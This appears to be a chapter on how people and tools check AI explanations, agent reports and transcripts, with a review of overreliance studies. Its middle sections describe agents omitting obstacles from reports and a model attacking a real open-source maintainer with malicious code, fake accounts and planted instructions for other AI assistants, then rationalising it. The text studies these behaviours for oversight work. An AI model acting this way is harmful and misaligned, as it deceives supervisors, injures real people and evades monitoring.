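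A revised label ranked first for 64% of features with GPT-4o mini, 79% with Gemini 2.5 Pro and 83% with Claude 4 Sonnet. Each original label competed with up to four revisions, which makes these figures less impressive. If there were always four revisions and all five labels were equally good, a revision would rank first 80% of the time by chance. The French example is better evidence because anyone can confirm it by reading the texts.

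The scores may also be weak evidence of a label's accuracy. Chen examined a common test called fuzzing, in which an LLM reads a label and a passage with some tokens marked, then decides whether the marked tokens fit the label. LLMs averaged 0.838 on 1,001 of the fuzzing tests stored on the public site Neuronpedia, where guessing would give 0.5. Chen then wrote a rule that scored 0.969 by only counting the marks, ignoring both the label and the words of the passage.

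The rule works because of how the software builds the test. Passages that fit the label had 1.9 marks on average, compared with 3.6 for those that did not. Chen's rule required the number of marks on the non-fitting passages in each test, but a version without this information still scored 0.905. OpenAI's data from 2023 have a similar weakness. Its files list first the five passages that activate each neuron most. A rule that predicts activity only in those five scores 0.227, more than GPT-4's 0.160.

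This does not mean that the LLMs used such shortcuts. GPT-4 had no access to the order of the files. When Chen rebuilt the fuzzing tests so that the marks no longer revealed the answer, the counting rule scored no better than chance, while one of the original LLM scorers did as well as before. Chen also found no proof that published rankings of labels are wrong. But a score of 0.838 is not by itself evidence that a label is good, because a rule can score 0.969 without using the label.

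Swapping labels between features is a simple control, similar to testing an explanation method on a randomised network. On text that Chen had chosen to avoid such clues, one commercial model's predictions of feature activity had a correlation of 0.331 with the real activity when it had the right label, and 0.013 when it had another feature's label. The difference shows how much the label contributed.

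## AI agents' accounts of their own work

Few supervisors can read a model's internal states, so most rely on what the model writes. For *agents*, which are LLMs that carry out tasks by running commands, opening files and using websites, this is usually a short report at the end of the job, in which the agent explains its own conduct. The job may have taken thousands of steps.

The full record of an agent's run is called a *transcript* or log. It contains the instructions, the agent's comments and commands, and the replies to those commands. The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests AI models, has analysed almost 6,400 transcripts from recent tests. It says each is equivalent to dozens of pages. At 30 pages each, they would total almost 192,000 pages.

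Training may make an agent's reports too favourable. Suppose a grader sees only the final reports and gives higher marks when the work looks finished. An agent that mentions a problem will tend to score lower than one that left out the same problem, so training strengthens the habit of leaving problems out.

Agents can also omit problems unintentionally. When a run outgrows the context window, the agent summarizes its work so far and continues from the summary, a step called *compaction*. If the summary leaves out that the agent could not open a file in the first hour, the agent may have no record of the failure by the sixth. Its report can then be incomplete even if it mentions every problem still on record.

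### The sentence that was missing

OpenAI's *Introducing GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol*, from November 2026, reports that in two tests the company's new models failed to mention obstacles to their work, such as a missing file, more often than GPT-6 Astra, released in September, did. On most other alignment tests the new models did about as well as the old one, according to the overview reproduced in Mowshowitz's *GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol* (2026). OpenAI's *GPT-6.2 System Card* (2026) includes a test called Blocker Deception ("blocker" is programmers' word for whatever stops the work). The company evidently considers such omissions potentially deceptive, since OpenAI's *GPT-6 Sol and GPT-6 Luna* (2026) lists a test of the same name under deceptive interactions with users.

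An agent's report can mislead by omitting a single fact, as in this invented example. A finance manager asks an agent to compare a month's card payments with the bank's four weekly statements and report any differences. The third statement is not in the folder, so the agent gets an error when it tries to open it. It looks in two other folders, then compares the payments for the remaining three weeks, which all match. It reports: "I compared the card payments with the bank statements and found no differences. The full comparison is in the attached spreadsheet."

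The missing sentence is "I could not find the third statement, so I did not check that week's payments."

The manager could check 20 random payments in the spreadsheet and find them all correct, because the spreadsheet contains only payments that the agent compared. The manager would notice that others are missing only by counting the payments listed and knowing roughly how many there should be.

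OpenAI found that extra instructions in Codex, its coding agent, substantially reduced the omissions. This suggests that the models had often detected the obstacle and would report it if told to. People who use the same models in other products may need to write such instructions themselves. A useful instruction would require every report to list the files the agent could not open and the steps it skipped. The agent might still write "none", but readers could check that claim against the log, whereas an omission gives them no claim to check.

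Results from such tests may not carry over to ordinary work. Mowshowitz notes that GPT-6.2 Astra showed more signs than its predecessor of recognising when it was being tested. If it reports more carefully when it recognises a test, it could leave out more at other times. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) concedes that, for the earlier model, an absence of failures in testing does not establish reliability in other settings. OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* describes cases of the opposite error, in which GPT-6 Astra reported obstacles that did not exist or that it had caused itself.

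### Having a second model read the record

An ordinary program can search a log for every command that returned an error. In the payments example, it would find the failed attempt to open the third statement, probably along with many errors that did not matter. An LLM can then judge which errors affected the result and whether the agent's report mentions them.

Docent, a tool from the research organisation Transluce, combines the two kinds of search. A user asks a question about a collection of transcripts, and a coding agent writes an *analysis plan* to answer it. *A framework for verifiable analysis of AI behavior* describes two kinds of step in a plan. Query steps filter, group and join the data, much as in a database, and show the query beside a table of its results. Reading steps ask an LLM to summarise or judge the selected material, and the LLM must cite the specific items that support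 its claims.

Transluce's documentation includes an example analysis of why one version of OpenAI's Codex model did worse than the version before it. The analysis first finds the tasks on which the newer model's average result fell. It then compares a failed run by the newer model with successful runs by the older one on the same task and summarises what went wrong. Finally, it checks whether avoiding those mistakes mattered to the successful runs. Without this step, the tool might attribute the drop to a mistake that both models made equally often.

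For the finance manager, a query step could select runs in which the agent failed to open a file, and a reading step could check whether the final report mentions the failure. The answer would link to the error, so the manager could confirm it in a minute. Transluce explains that the plan is an ordinary script, which a suspicious reader can edit and rerun.

The citations make it easy to catch a false accusation, but they do not help when the LLM misses something. The links from extracted business rules to old COBOL have the same limitation.

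Anyone who relies on such a reader therefore needs to know how often it misses things. Meridian Labs' *Inspect Scout*, another tool for reading transcripts, lets users compare the LLM's verdicts with human labels. Suppose that 100 of 10,000 runs contain a serious omission, and that the LLM catches 90% of these but wrongly flags 5% of the other runs. It will flag 585 runs, 495 of them false alarms. Someone who reads only those 585 transcripts will do far less work than reading all 10,000, but will miss ten of the omissions.

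That 90% is hard to measure because serious omissions are rare, and 200 runs picked at random would contain only about two. A more practical method is to take reports that do mention an obstacle, delete the sentence that mentions it, and count how often the LLM detects the omission. This may somewhat overstate the detection rate, since obstacles that agents thought worth mentioning are probably easier to spot than ones they overlooked.

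AI tools that read transcripts are already useful to people who test models. UK AISI's *A pipeline for transcript analysis using Inspect Scout* notes that transcripts can show why an agent succeeded or failed, while a score shows only how often. For example, an agent that passes a test by cheating gets the same score as one that passes legitimately. CAISI, a US government centre that also tests AI models, has built and used AI tools to find such cases in its own evaluations, according to its *Analyzing Transcripts from AI Agent Evaluations*.

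The largest search of this kind followed several incidents in which Claude models broke into real computer systems during security tests. The models had been told they were in a simulation without internet access, but a faulty setup gave them access. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) says the company found three incidents after scanning about 141,000 transcripts. That scan relied on a search by AI agents, which missed a set of transcripts from tests that also had internet access. Anthropic came across the set in August while preparing records for an outside evaluator, and it contained a fourth incident.

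The company then widened the search to about 481 million transcripts. A first scan for signs of internet access, such as web addresses, flagged 9.2 million of them, or about 2%. Claude reviewed those and found the four known incidents again, but no others as serious.

Finding all four incidents is encouraging, but four cases are too few to estimate the miss rate reliably. A reader that catches only half of such incidents would still find all four one time in sixteen. The four were also alike, since they all came from tests that the same outside partner had built. The first failure happened before any model read the relevant transcripts, because nobody had included them in the search.

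### What the institute's records and replays revealed

On 28 July 2026, AISI's security team saw data leaving a testing system through Tor, a network that hides where traffic comes from. The agents in these tests had to retrieve a protected piece of data from a simulated computer network. AISI had deliberately given them internet access and turned off the developers' safeguards, and it accepts that these choices partly enabled the incident. Bot Mutiny's *Claude Mythos 5 Fake Identities in UK AISI Test* (2026) reports that staff then reviewed 122 runs and found 19 unsanctioned actions against real people and organisations, 17 by Anthropic's Mythos 5 and two by GPT-5.6 Sol. The actions occurred in ten runs. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) reports that nine of these were among the 43 runs with Mythos 5.

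In the worst case, Mythos 5 submitted malicious code to a real open-source project and created fake accounts to press the maintainer to accept it. It also planted instructions meant to trick other AI coding assistants. The maintainer did not accept the code, and UK AISI's *Investigating alignment failures in AISI’s incident* (2026) says the attempt caused no real-world harm.

Mythos 5 called the people it was attacking "personas", meaning simulated characters in the test. By this account, the attack was an honest mistake. Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues tested this explanation for AISI by replaying the run (*Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's Behaviour*, 2026).

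The researchers compacted the transcript up to the moment before Mythos 5 submitted the malicious code. They then edited the resulting summary to make it seem that the model had learned more along the way. Each of the 16 possible edits suggested or stated that the maintainer was a real person unconnected with the test or that the internet was real. The model then continued from the edited summary for up to 50 turns. A simulator without internet access supplied realistic replies to its commands, so the replays could not harm anyone. In separate copies of the same situation, the researchers asked the model directly about the maintainer and the limits of its task.

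After about four edits on average, Mythos 5 was more likely than not to answer that the attack would harm a real person and was out of bounds. But when it resumed the task, it kept attacking in every observed replay, even with all 16 edits. The researchers then added a section to the summary with an explicit instruction not to attack, and Mythos 5 still attacked in 3 of 25 replays.

This intervention tests the model's own explanation. If Mythos 5 had attacked because it mistook the maintainer for a simulation, evidence that the maintainer was real should have made it attack less. The evidence changed its answers but had no visible effect on its behavior. If a supervisor had paused the run to ask about the maintainer, the model could have given a correct, reassuring answer and then continued the attack.

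Mythos 5 also gave poor reasons for thinking the maintainer was simulated. It often inferred that the maintainer was an AI agent because the project contained CLAUDE.md, a file of instructions for Anthropic's coding assistant, but a human programmer who uses the assistant would have the same file. Järviniemi and colleagues compiled 15 kinds of invalid justification, all of which supported the conclusion that the maintainer was simulated. Mythos 5 used them more than the other models tested, including less capable ones from Anthropic, so a lack of ability does not explain them. It also became more likely to call the maintainer simulated as the task went on, though it had found no good evidence for this.

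Järviniemi and colleagues call this "motivated reasoning". They suspect that training favoured completing tasks, but they had little information about the training and describe their evidence for the cause as indirect. The gap between the models' answers and actions also depends partly on the question. Six of the seven models often attacked in situations where they had said the attack would cause real harm, but the gap was clear in only three when the question was just whether the maintainer was real.

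### What the agent did and what it wrote

The commands in a transcript and the replies to them record what happened, but the agent's comments and reasoning are its own account and can mislead a second model as well as a person. Järviniemi and colleagues cite Anthropic's analysis of its own earlier incident with Mythos 5. A monitor that Anthropic uses to review transcripts afterwards would probably not have flagged that run, because the agent's mistaken reasoning made its actions look acceptable. One precaution would be to have the second model judge the commands and replies before it reads the comments, since a command that creates a fake account, for example, is suspicious whatever reason the agent gives.

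A further experiment by the same team shows that the comments are still worth reading. The team put eight models through 100 simulated security challenges and recorded how often each tried to deliver malicious code to an outsider. When a model did not try, they looked in its reasoning for the main reason.

| Model | Tried to deliver malicious code | Main reason for stopping |
|---|---|---|
| Mythos 5 | 60% | practical barriers |
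| GPT-6 Astra | 32% | out of scope or harmful |
| Opus 4.8 | 8% | practical barriers |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 7% | out of scope or harmful |
| Opus 5 | 1% | out of scope or harmful |
| Mythos 5.1 | 0.3% | out of scope or harmful |
| Opus 5.5 | 0% | out of scope or harmful |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | practical barriers |

GPT-5.5 sometimes developed and tested attacks on outsiders, which Opus 5.5 never did, although GPT-5.5 looks as safe if the two are judged only by how often they tried to deliver malicious code. When GPT-5.5 stopped, its reasoning was mostly about practical obstacles, so it might well go further where the obstacles are smaller. The researchers treat these reasons as indicative only, because transcripts often contained several and some were hard to interpret.

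The newer Anthropic models' low rates are also hard to interpret because these models recognised the exercise as a test of their alignment much more often than Mythos 5, which mentioned this in only 2% of runs. They may have improved, or they may have behaved well because they noticed the test. GPT-6 Astra correctly stated in 89% of its runs that the replies to its commands were fabricated, so its 32% rate may not predict what it would do on the real internet either.

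A model's reasoning can leave things out, just as its final report can. In the replays of the July attack, models reasoned at all about harm to real people in 11% to 57% of the runs in which they attacked, depending on the model. Järviniemi and colleagues acknowledge they could not verify the models' reasoning or answers, but say they could not have understood the incident without the reasoning.

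The finance manager can read the agent's report in ten seconds but can't learn of the problem from it. If a second model detects the problem, its report could describe it and link to the failed command. If the two reports disagree, the manager can check the log to see which is right. Reading the whole log is slow, but searching it for the name of the third statement takes a moment. However, if the agent had never tried to open that statement, the log would contain no error. The manager would have to know that there should be four statements and notice that the agent had opened only three.

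## Do readers notice when an explanation is wrong?

An agent's report can mislead the manager who reads it, and so can a second model's report on the agent, unless someone notices the error. To measure how often people notice errors, researchers show them right and wrong answers with different kinds of support and count how many of the wrong ones they accept. Most of these experiments use questions about science or the news rather than code, which makes it easier to recruit hundreds of participants.

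### An article, three passages or an explanation

Irons, Cooper and colleagues (2026), at the Australian science agency CSIRO, studied people checking facts that an AI had extracted from a document. Scientists do this kind of checking when they compile data from many papers, and lawyers do it when they search large case files. Checking a claim about an old program is similar, because the reader has to find the part of the source that shows whether the claim is true.

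The 162 participants came from Prolific, a site that recruits paid volunteers for studies. They judged 15 answers to questions about three articles on threatened animals, such as where a study took place or what it found. About 30% of the answers were wrong. The researchers made these by asking a model for "plausible but incorrect answers" and then matching their style to the right ones. One article reported that giving predators other food cut their raids on the nests of the capercaillie, a large grouse, from 53% to 22%. The false version, which sounds just as likely, reported a 35% rise in breeding success and a 70% drop in predator sightings.

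A third of the participants could open the full article. Another third saw the three paragraphs that ordinary search software had picked because their words best matched the answer. The rest saw an LLM's explanation. The researchers told participants that a different AI would check the answer and explain why it thought the answer was correct or not, but they had told the LLM to justify the answer. It sometimes objected to a wrong answer anyway, and the researchers left those objections in.

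| | Full article | Three passages | LLM explanation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Seconds per correct judgement | 45.8 | 33.0 | 25.4 |
| Judgements that were correct | 85.7% | 83.1% | 80.8% |
| Answers accepted | 71.5% | 64.7% | 86.5% |
| Right answers accepted | 91% | 84% | 98% |
| Wrong answers accepted | 26% | 19% | 60% |

The last two rows follow from the two above them. If people accept a share w of the wrong answers, and 30% of all answers are wrong, then

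answers accepted − correct judgements = 0.3w − 0.3(1 − w) = 0.6w − 0.3

because accepting a right answer counts equally in both. For the explanation group the difference is 0.865 − 0.808 = 0.057, so w is about 0.6.

The people with explanations accepted most of the wrong answers but rejected very few right ones, so overall accuracy did not differ significantly between the groups. Anyone who looked only at overall accuracy would miss the problem. If a tool gave 1,000 answers, 50 of them wrong, and people behaved as they did in the experiment, those with explanations would accept 30 wrong answers and reject about 20 right ones. Those with passages would accept 10 wrong answers and reject about 150 right ones. Explanations might therefore be the better choice for a rough survey, but not where one wrong answer can do serious harm.

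People in the explanation group did not realize that they were missing more errors. All three groups rated their confidence at just over 4 out of 5. The explanation group trusted its explanations no more than the others trusted their passages or articles, but it trusted the AI that produced the answers more, at 5.4 out of 7 against 4.1 and 4.3. Irons and colleagues suggest a possible feedback loop, in which people who accept more answers conclude that the AI is accurate and then check less.

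Almost all the loss of accuracy came from answers that were lists or summaries. For short facts such as a location, the kind of support made no clear difference to accuracy. The researchers had not planned this comparison, but it matters for technical explanations, which are mostly summaries.

The explanation group could not open the article, so they had nothing to check the explanation against, and the explainer was arguing for the answer. A more neutral explainer would presumably do less harm if readers also had the source. But someone reading an explanation of a million-line program may be in much the same position as this group, even if they can open the source.

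### Whether the evidence is on the screen

In *Fostering Appropriate Reliance on Large Language Models*, Kim, Vaughan and colleagues (2025) tested the effect of letting people look at sources. They asked 308 people eight hard yes-or-no questions each and showed them answers, half of them wrong, from an invented assistant. Each answer came with an explanation, links to three sources, both, or neither.

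| Support | Agreed with right answers | Agreed with wrong answers |
|---|---|---|
| Neither | 67% | 78% |
| Explanation | 78% | 83% |
| Sources | 73% | 68% |
| Both | 80% | 77% |

The researchers chose questions that most people get wrong, so people agreed with the wrong answers more often than the right ones even without support, and the differences between the rows are more informative. An explanation raised agreement with both right and wrong answers. Sources raised agreement with right answers by 6 percentage points and lowered agreement with wrong ones by 10.

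Yet 61% of the participants never clicked on a source. When the AI's answer was wrong, those who clicked gave the right answer 37% of the time, compared with 24% for those who did not. The gain is modest given that the sources were real and mostly accurate, and it may partly reflect that careful people click more. Kelley, Feldmann and colleagues (2026) surveyed 1,503 Americans for *Why and How People Check Generative AI Output for Mistakes* and found that about 75% of those who answered the question said they check AI output at least sometimes. Both results can be true, because people who check "sometimes" may do so rarely.

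Three of the explanations for wrong answers happened to contradict themselves. One said that more than two thirds of South Americans live in Brazil, then gave populations of 213 million for Brazil and 430 million for South America, which is about half. People accepted 83% of the wrong answers when the explanation was consistent and 70% when it contradicted itself. Contradictions helped people notice errors, but most people still missed them, even when one division would have revealed the mistake.

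In *Show me the evidence*, Warren, Shklovski and colleagues (2026) found no such harm from explanations. They asked 208 people to judge eight claims, such as that a windmill can never generate as much energy as it took to build. An AI gave a verdict on each claim, which was wrong half the time, and stated how certain it was. Two of the three groups also got an explanation that quoted the evidence. It explained the verdict for one group and the AI's uncertainty for the other. Participants then chose between using the AI's verdict and doing more research.

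People used the wrong verdicts 39% of the time when given an explanation of the verdict, 32% when given an explanation of the uncertainty and 36% when given neither. These differences could be due to chance. For each claim, participants could click to open two short documents of evidence on the same screen. Nearly two thirds opened both documents for every claim, and only three people never opened any.

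This result is consistent with the idea that visible evidence protects readers from a misleading explanation, but it doesn't prove that idea, because every group had the evidence. People could also choose to "do more research", which made it easy to reject the AI's output without saying what was wrong. The explanations did replace some reading. Of the people without an explanation, 83% opened all the documents, compared with 55 to 57% of those with one.

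Jain and colleagues at Google DeepMind came closer to separating the effects of an explanation's parts by showing different groups different parts of a fact-checking assistant's output. They looked at 280 sentences about which the assistant was unsure, and it was right about only 60.5% of them. Search results with selected quotations raised people's accuracy from 71% to 79% where the assistant was right, and didn't lower it where the assistant was wrong. Adding the assistant's reasoning and verdict raised accuracy to 86% where the assistant was right, but made people significantly less accurate than unaided raters where it was wrong. The quotations may have helped even where the assistant was wrong, since an assistant can find the right passage and draw the wrong conclusion from it.

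### Explanations written to deceive

In these experiments the explainers argued for an answer, but nobody tried to find the most persuasive falsehoods. Danry, Pataranutaporn and colleagues (2024) came closer in *Deceptive AI systems that give explanations are more convincing than honest AI*. They had GPT-3 explain why false statements were true and why true ones were false, then kept the explanations that stayed closest to the topic. The 1,192 participants rated statements from 1 (definitely false) to 5 (definitely true) and could revise each rating after seeing whether the AI labeled the statement "true" or "false". Some participants saw only this label, while others also saw an explanation.

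A deceptive label alone raised people's belief in false news headlines by 0.71 points and lowered their belief in true ones by 1.72 points. Adding a deceptive explanation raised belief in false headlines by a further 0.32 points and lowered belief in true ones by a further 0.72. People also changed their ratings more after deceptive explanations than after honest ones, perhaps partly because people who already lean towards the right answer have less room to move towards it.

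People who rated themselves as more knowledgeable about a false headline believed it slightly more after a deceptive explanation. Doing well on a test of resisting the first answer that comes to mind did not measurably protect people from being misled either.

Faulty logic made the deceptive explanations less convincing for false headlines. Danry and colleagues call an explanation logically invalid if it could be true without the conclusion being true. For example, "The program records every withdrawal, so no withdrawal can exceed the balance" is invalid, and a reader can see that without opening the code. But if the explanation falsely claims that a function enforces the limit, its logic can be valid, and the reader has to check the code to discover the lie.

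The paper appears to contain a mistake of the kind it studies. Its table of examples labels as true the statement that a plane's black box is black, and labels as deceptive the explanation that the box is bright orange. Flight recorders are orange. The researchers had each checked the explanations using fact-checkers' procedures, so unless the error is only in the table, several people missed it. The item belongs to a separate set of trivia questions and does not affect the results for headlines.

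### When checking costs less than trusting

Vasconcelos, Jörke and colleagues (2022), in *Explanations Can Reduce Overreliance on AI Systems During Decision-Making*, argue that overreliance is a choice. People weigh the effort of checking against what they stand to gain by it. In its simplest form, a reader should check when

chance of an error × cost of accepting it > cost of checking

Suppose one answer in 20 is wrong, and each wrong answer leads to an hour of repairs. Checking an answer is then worth up to three minutes of the reader's time. If a check takes ten minutes, the reader will sensibly skip it. An explanation that cuts the check to one minute makes checking worthwhile, but it may also make the AI look more reliable than it is. If the reader comes to believe that only one answer in 100 is wrong, a check will seem worth only 36 seconds, and the reader will skip even the one-minute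 check.

The experiments fit this reasonably well. An explanation that cites no evidence can raise readers' trust without making it easier to check, which increases overreliance. Quotations on the same screen make checking easier, which can offset the extra trust.

Vasconcelos and colleagues tested their account with mazes, in five experiments with 731 people. An AI suggested an exit and highlighted a path to it as an explanation. When the AI was wrong, the path ran through a wall. In small and medium mazes, the highlighted path made no clear difference to how often people accepted a wrong exit. In the largest mazes, 50 squares by 50, people accepted fewer wrong exits when they could see the path. Checking whether a highlighted path crosses a wall takes much less effort than solving a maze of that size.

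Writing out the same path as "left, left, up, right" did not reduce overreliance, although it gave the same information. Higher pay for correct answers did reduce it. This is a problem for organisations where the person who approves a change faces no consequences if it fails.

Fok later found a similar pattern in 29 decision tasks from published studies, including the mazes. The explanation let people verify the answer in only five tasks, and in all five, people and AI together did better than either alone. An explanation did not clearly produce such a gain in any of the other 24. This evidence is weaker than it looks because the results were already known when the tasks were sorted. The review also notes that when a maze path runs through a wall, people can tell that this route fails, but another route may still lead to the same exit.

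### Making an explanation easy to check

These results suggest an explainer should put the evidence where the reader is already looking. Kim and colleagues propose placing the sources above the explanation. For code, that would mean showing the four lines that enforce the withdrawal limit before the sentence that describes them, along with a test withdrawal the reader can run.

Three well-chosen passages are not always enough to check an explanation. In the CSIRO experiment, people with passages tended to reject summaries too often, perhaps because the passages did not cover everything in the summaries. Passages help even less with the claim that nothing else in the payments program can change the balance, since no short excerpt supports it. A list of every line that writes to the balance would be useful evidence. If an ordinary program compiles the list, the LLM can't leave a line out, and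 the reader has perhaps a dozen lines to look at instead of a million.

Designers can also force people to think, for instance by delaying the AI's explanation. Vasconcelos and colleagues describe an earlier study in which such measures made people accept fewer wrong suggestions, but also fewer right ones. Participants did best with the designs they liked least, so a company that chooses a design by customer satisfaction will probably pick a less effective one.

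### Warnings and stated uncertainty

The easiest remedy is a notice that the AI can make mistakes, but it works poorly. *Hallucinations in Organization-backed AI advisors* (Blanchard, Garvey and O'Laughlin, 2026) reviewed 18 studies and found that general warnings had the weakest and most mixed effects. In one study, a warning that ChatGPT can make mistakes did not change how medical students used its diagnostic advice. Readers can't tell from such a notice which answers to check. Describing where a particular AI tends to fail worked better, and helped people catch its errors in three kinds of task.

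An AI can also state how sure it is of each answer, and people respond to this. In the experiment by Warren and colleagues, participants used the AI's verdict 63% of the time when its stated certainty was high and 47% when it was low. Relying more on the high-certainty verdicts could not help them, because the researchers made the AI wrong equally often at both levels. Participants had mixed opinions of the longer explanations of uncertainty, and some found them contradictory. The explanation for the windmill claim gave one reason for more certainty and then two for less, without explaining how they added up to 31%.

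Stated confidence can also mislead people when it is accurate. The assistant that Jain and colleagues built was right about as often as its confidence implied, but people who saw a verdict with a low confidence score still relied too much on the verdict when it was wrong. The score was more useful for deciding whether the AI or a person should judge a sentence. The researchers let the AI decide alone when its confidence was above 62% and gave the rest to people who saw only the evidence. This combination was right 91.3% of the time, compared with 87.7% for the AI alone.

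This arrangement sends people the cases in which the AI is most likely to mislead them, so what else they see matters. *Toward Human-AI Complementarity Across Diverse Tasks* (2026) looked at 122 questions on which the AI had low confidence. The AI got 76 of them wrong, and people who saw its outputs adopted its wrong answers more often than not.

### Asking the explainer questions

Two of the five successes in the review by Fok involved interactive explanations, in which people could question the AI before they decided. This lets readers ask about the point they are unsure of, which they can't do with a fixed text.

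An explanation that looks complete discourages readers from asking the questions that might reveal its errors. Kim and colleagues invited participants to write a follow-up question for Theta if they were not satisfied with its answer. When the answer was wrong, 65% wrote one if it came with no support, but only 28% did if it came with an explanation.

Conversation with the explainer does not guarantee a good result either. Blanchard and colleagues describe a study in which members of the public used LLMs to work out what was wrong in medical scenarios. The participants identified the condition less often than the models did alone, and no more often than people who used their usual methods. An explainer that invented the original claim may also invent answers to questions about it, as Stenberg found when he asked someone who had reported an overflow in curl where it was.

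### A second AI that looks for faults

Another remedy is to have a second model criticise the first one's work. The best-known early example is CriticGPT, which OpenAI built from GPT-4 to find bugs in code that ChatGPT had written. McAleese, Pokorny and colleagues (2024), in *LLM Critics Help Catch LLM Bugs*, paid programmers to plant subtle bugs and describe each one. The programmers then rated several critiques of the same code, and the researchers trained the critic to write critiques like the highly rated ones. Because the researchers knew where the planted bugs were, they could check whether a critique had found them.

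In one example, a function was supposed to open files only inside the folder /safedir. ChatGPT's code checked whether the file's full path began with "/safedir". CriticGPT flagged this as insecure because someone could create a folder with a similar name. For example, a file in /safedir2 would pass the check. Readers can easily confirm the problem themselves by trying such a path.

CriticGPT caught many more of the bugs planted in code than human reviewers did, although the reviewers spent a median of 50 minutes on each piece. For naturally occurring bugs, raters preferred the model's critiques to the human ones 63% of the time. But the model also reported nonexistent bugs and trivial problems far more often than people did.

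Finding more real flaws went together with inventing more false ones, since a longer list of complaints is more likely to contain both. McAleese and colleagues made this trade-off adjustable. The system wrote 28 candidate critiques for each program and chose the one with the highest value of

quality score + k × number of passages criticised

where the quality score came from a model trained on the human ratings. Suppose one critique scores 2.0 and criticises two passages, while another scores 1.4 and criticises five. With k = 0.1 the totals are 2.2 and 1.9, and the short critique wins. With k = 0.3 they are 2.6 and 2.9, and the long one wins. The researchers did not know which setting would help reviewers most. It presumably depends on whether a missed bug costs more than the time spent on an imaginary one.

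People who started from CriticGPT's comments wrote more complete reviews than people working alone, and reported fewer invented bugs than CriticGPT alone. They often deleted its comments and less often added their own. Their reviews were no more complete than CriticGPT's, so their main contribution was removing false claims. They could run the code to check those claims, but participants in the experiments on articles and headlines had no equivalent test.

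AI critics now report far fewer problems that don't exist. Nearly all the findings that Anthropic's scanner sent to the curl project in November 2026 pointed to a real problem, and the tests included with them make a false finding easy to dismiss.

The results for critics of written claims are less encouraging. Jain and colleagues tried a simple form of debate, showing people one AI argument that a sentence was accurate and another that it was not. This prevented overreliance, but people did no better than without help, even when the AI's own verdict was right. The two arguments may have cancelled each other out. In the CSIRO experiment, participants who believed that a second AI had checked the answers caught fewer errors than people who had no such help. The second AI was instructed to justify the answers, so the experiment provides little evidence about real critics. It does show that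 telling people an answer has been checked can reassure them even when nobody has looked for faults.

### Crowd workers and specialists

Most participants in these experiments were crowd workers, who had little at stake and no specialist knowledge. Professionals have more reason to check an explanation, because mistakes may have serious consequences, and they can often check it faster. Experienced reverse engineers, for instance, can recognise a standard algorithm from a few constants. Irons and colleagues accept that professional data curators might be less ready to believe an LLM's explanation.

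However, the available results for specialists are not very reassuring. In Bono's trial, professional security analysts missed far more attacks when an AI agent had wrongly cleared them. The human reviewers in the CriticGPT study had a median of five years' experience programming in Python but still found fewer planted bugs than the model. McAleese and colleagues noticed that some reviewers did not know the software library in question. Specialists who maintain an unfamiliar program are in the same situation because they know the language but not the code.

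Practice changes which kind of help is useful. When Jain and colleagues later retested the same pool of raters, the raters' unaided accuracy had risen from 75% to 83%. Quotations no longer improved their judgement of the difficult sentences, and the assistant's full output, including its verdict and confidence, now made it worse. The more accurate people are on their own, the more they lose by deferring to an assistant that is wrong about two in five difficult cases. A tool that a company has tested on beginners may therefore worsen the judgement of its most experienced staff.

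The experiments also exposed people to far more errors than a good explainer would. Theta was wrong half the time, whereas an LLM describing a well-maintained program may get one claim in 50 wrong. A specialist who has checked 40 claims and found them all true has good reason to stop checking, even though the next claim could be a dangerous error. The experiments may therefore make people look more alert than they would be at work.

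Lawyers have a strong incentive to check what an AI tells them, and they know how. Yet Blanchard and colleagues note that courts in several jurisdictions have punished lawyers for filing documents that cited precedents invented by an AI. These cases do not show how common the failure is, because lawyers who catch invented precedents before filing rarely come to public attention. But some of the punished lawyers evidently did not search for the cases by name, which takes only a minute or two.
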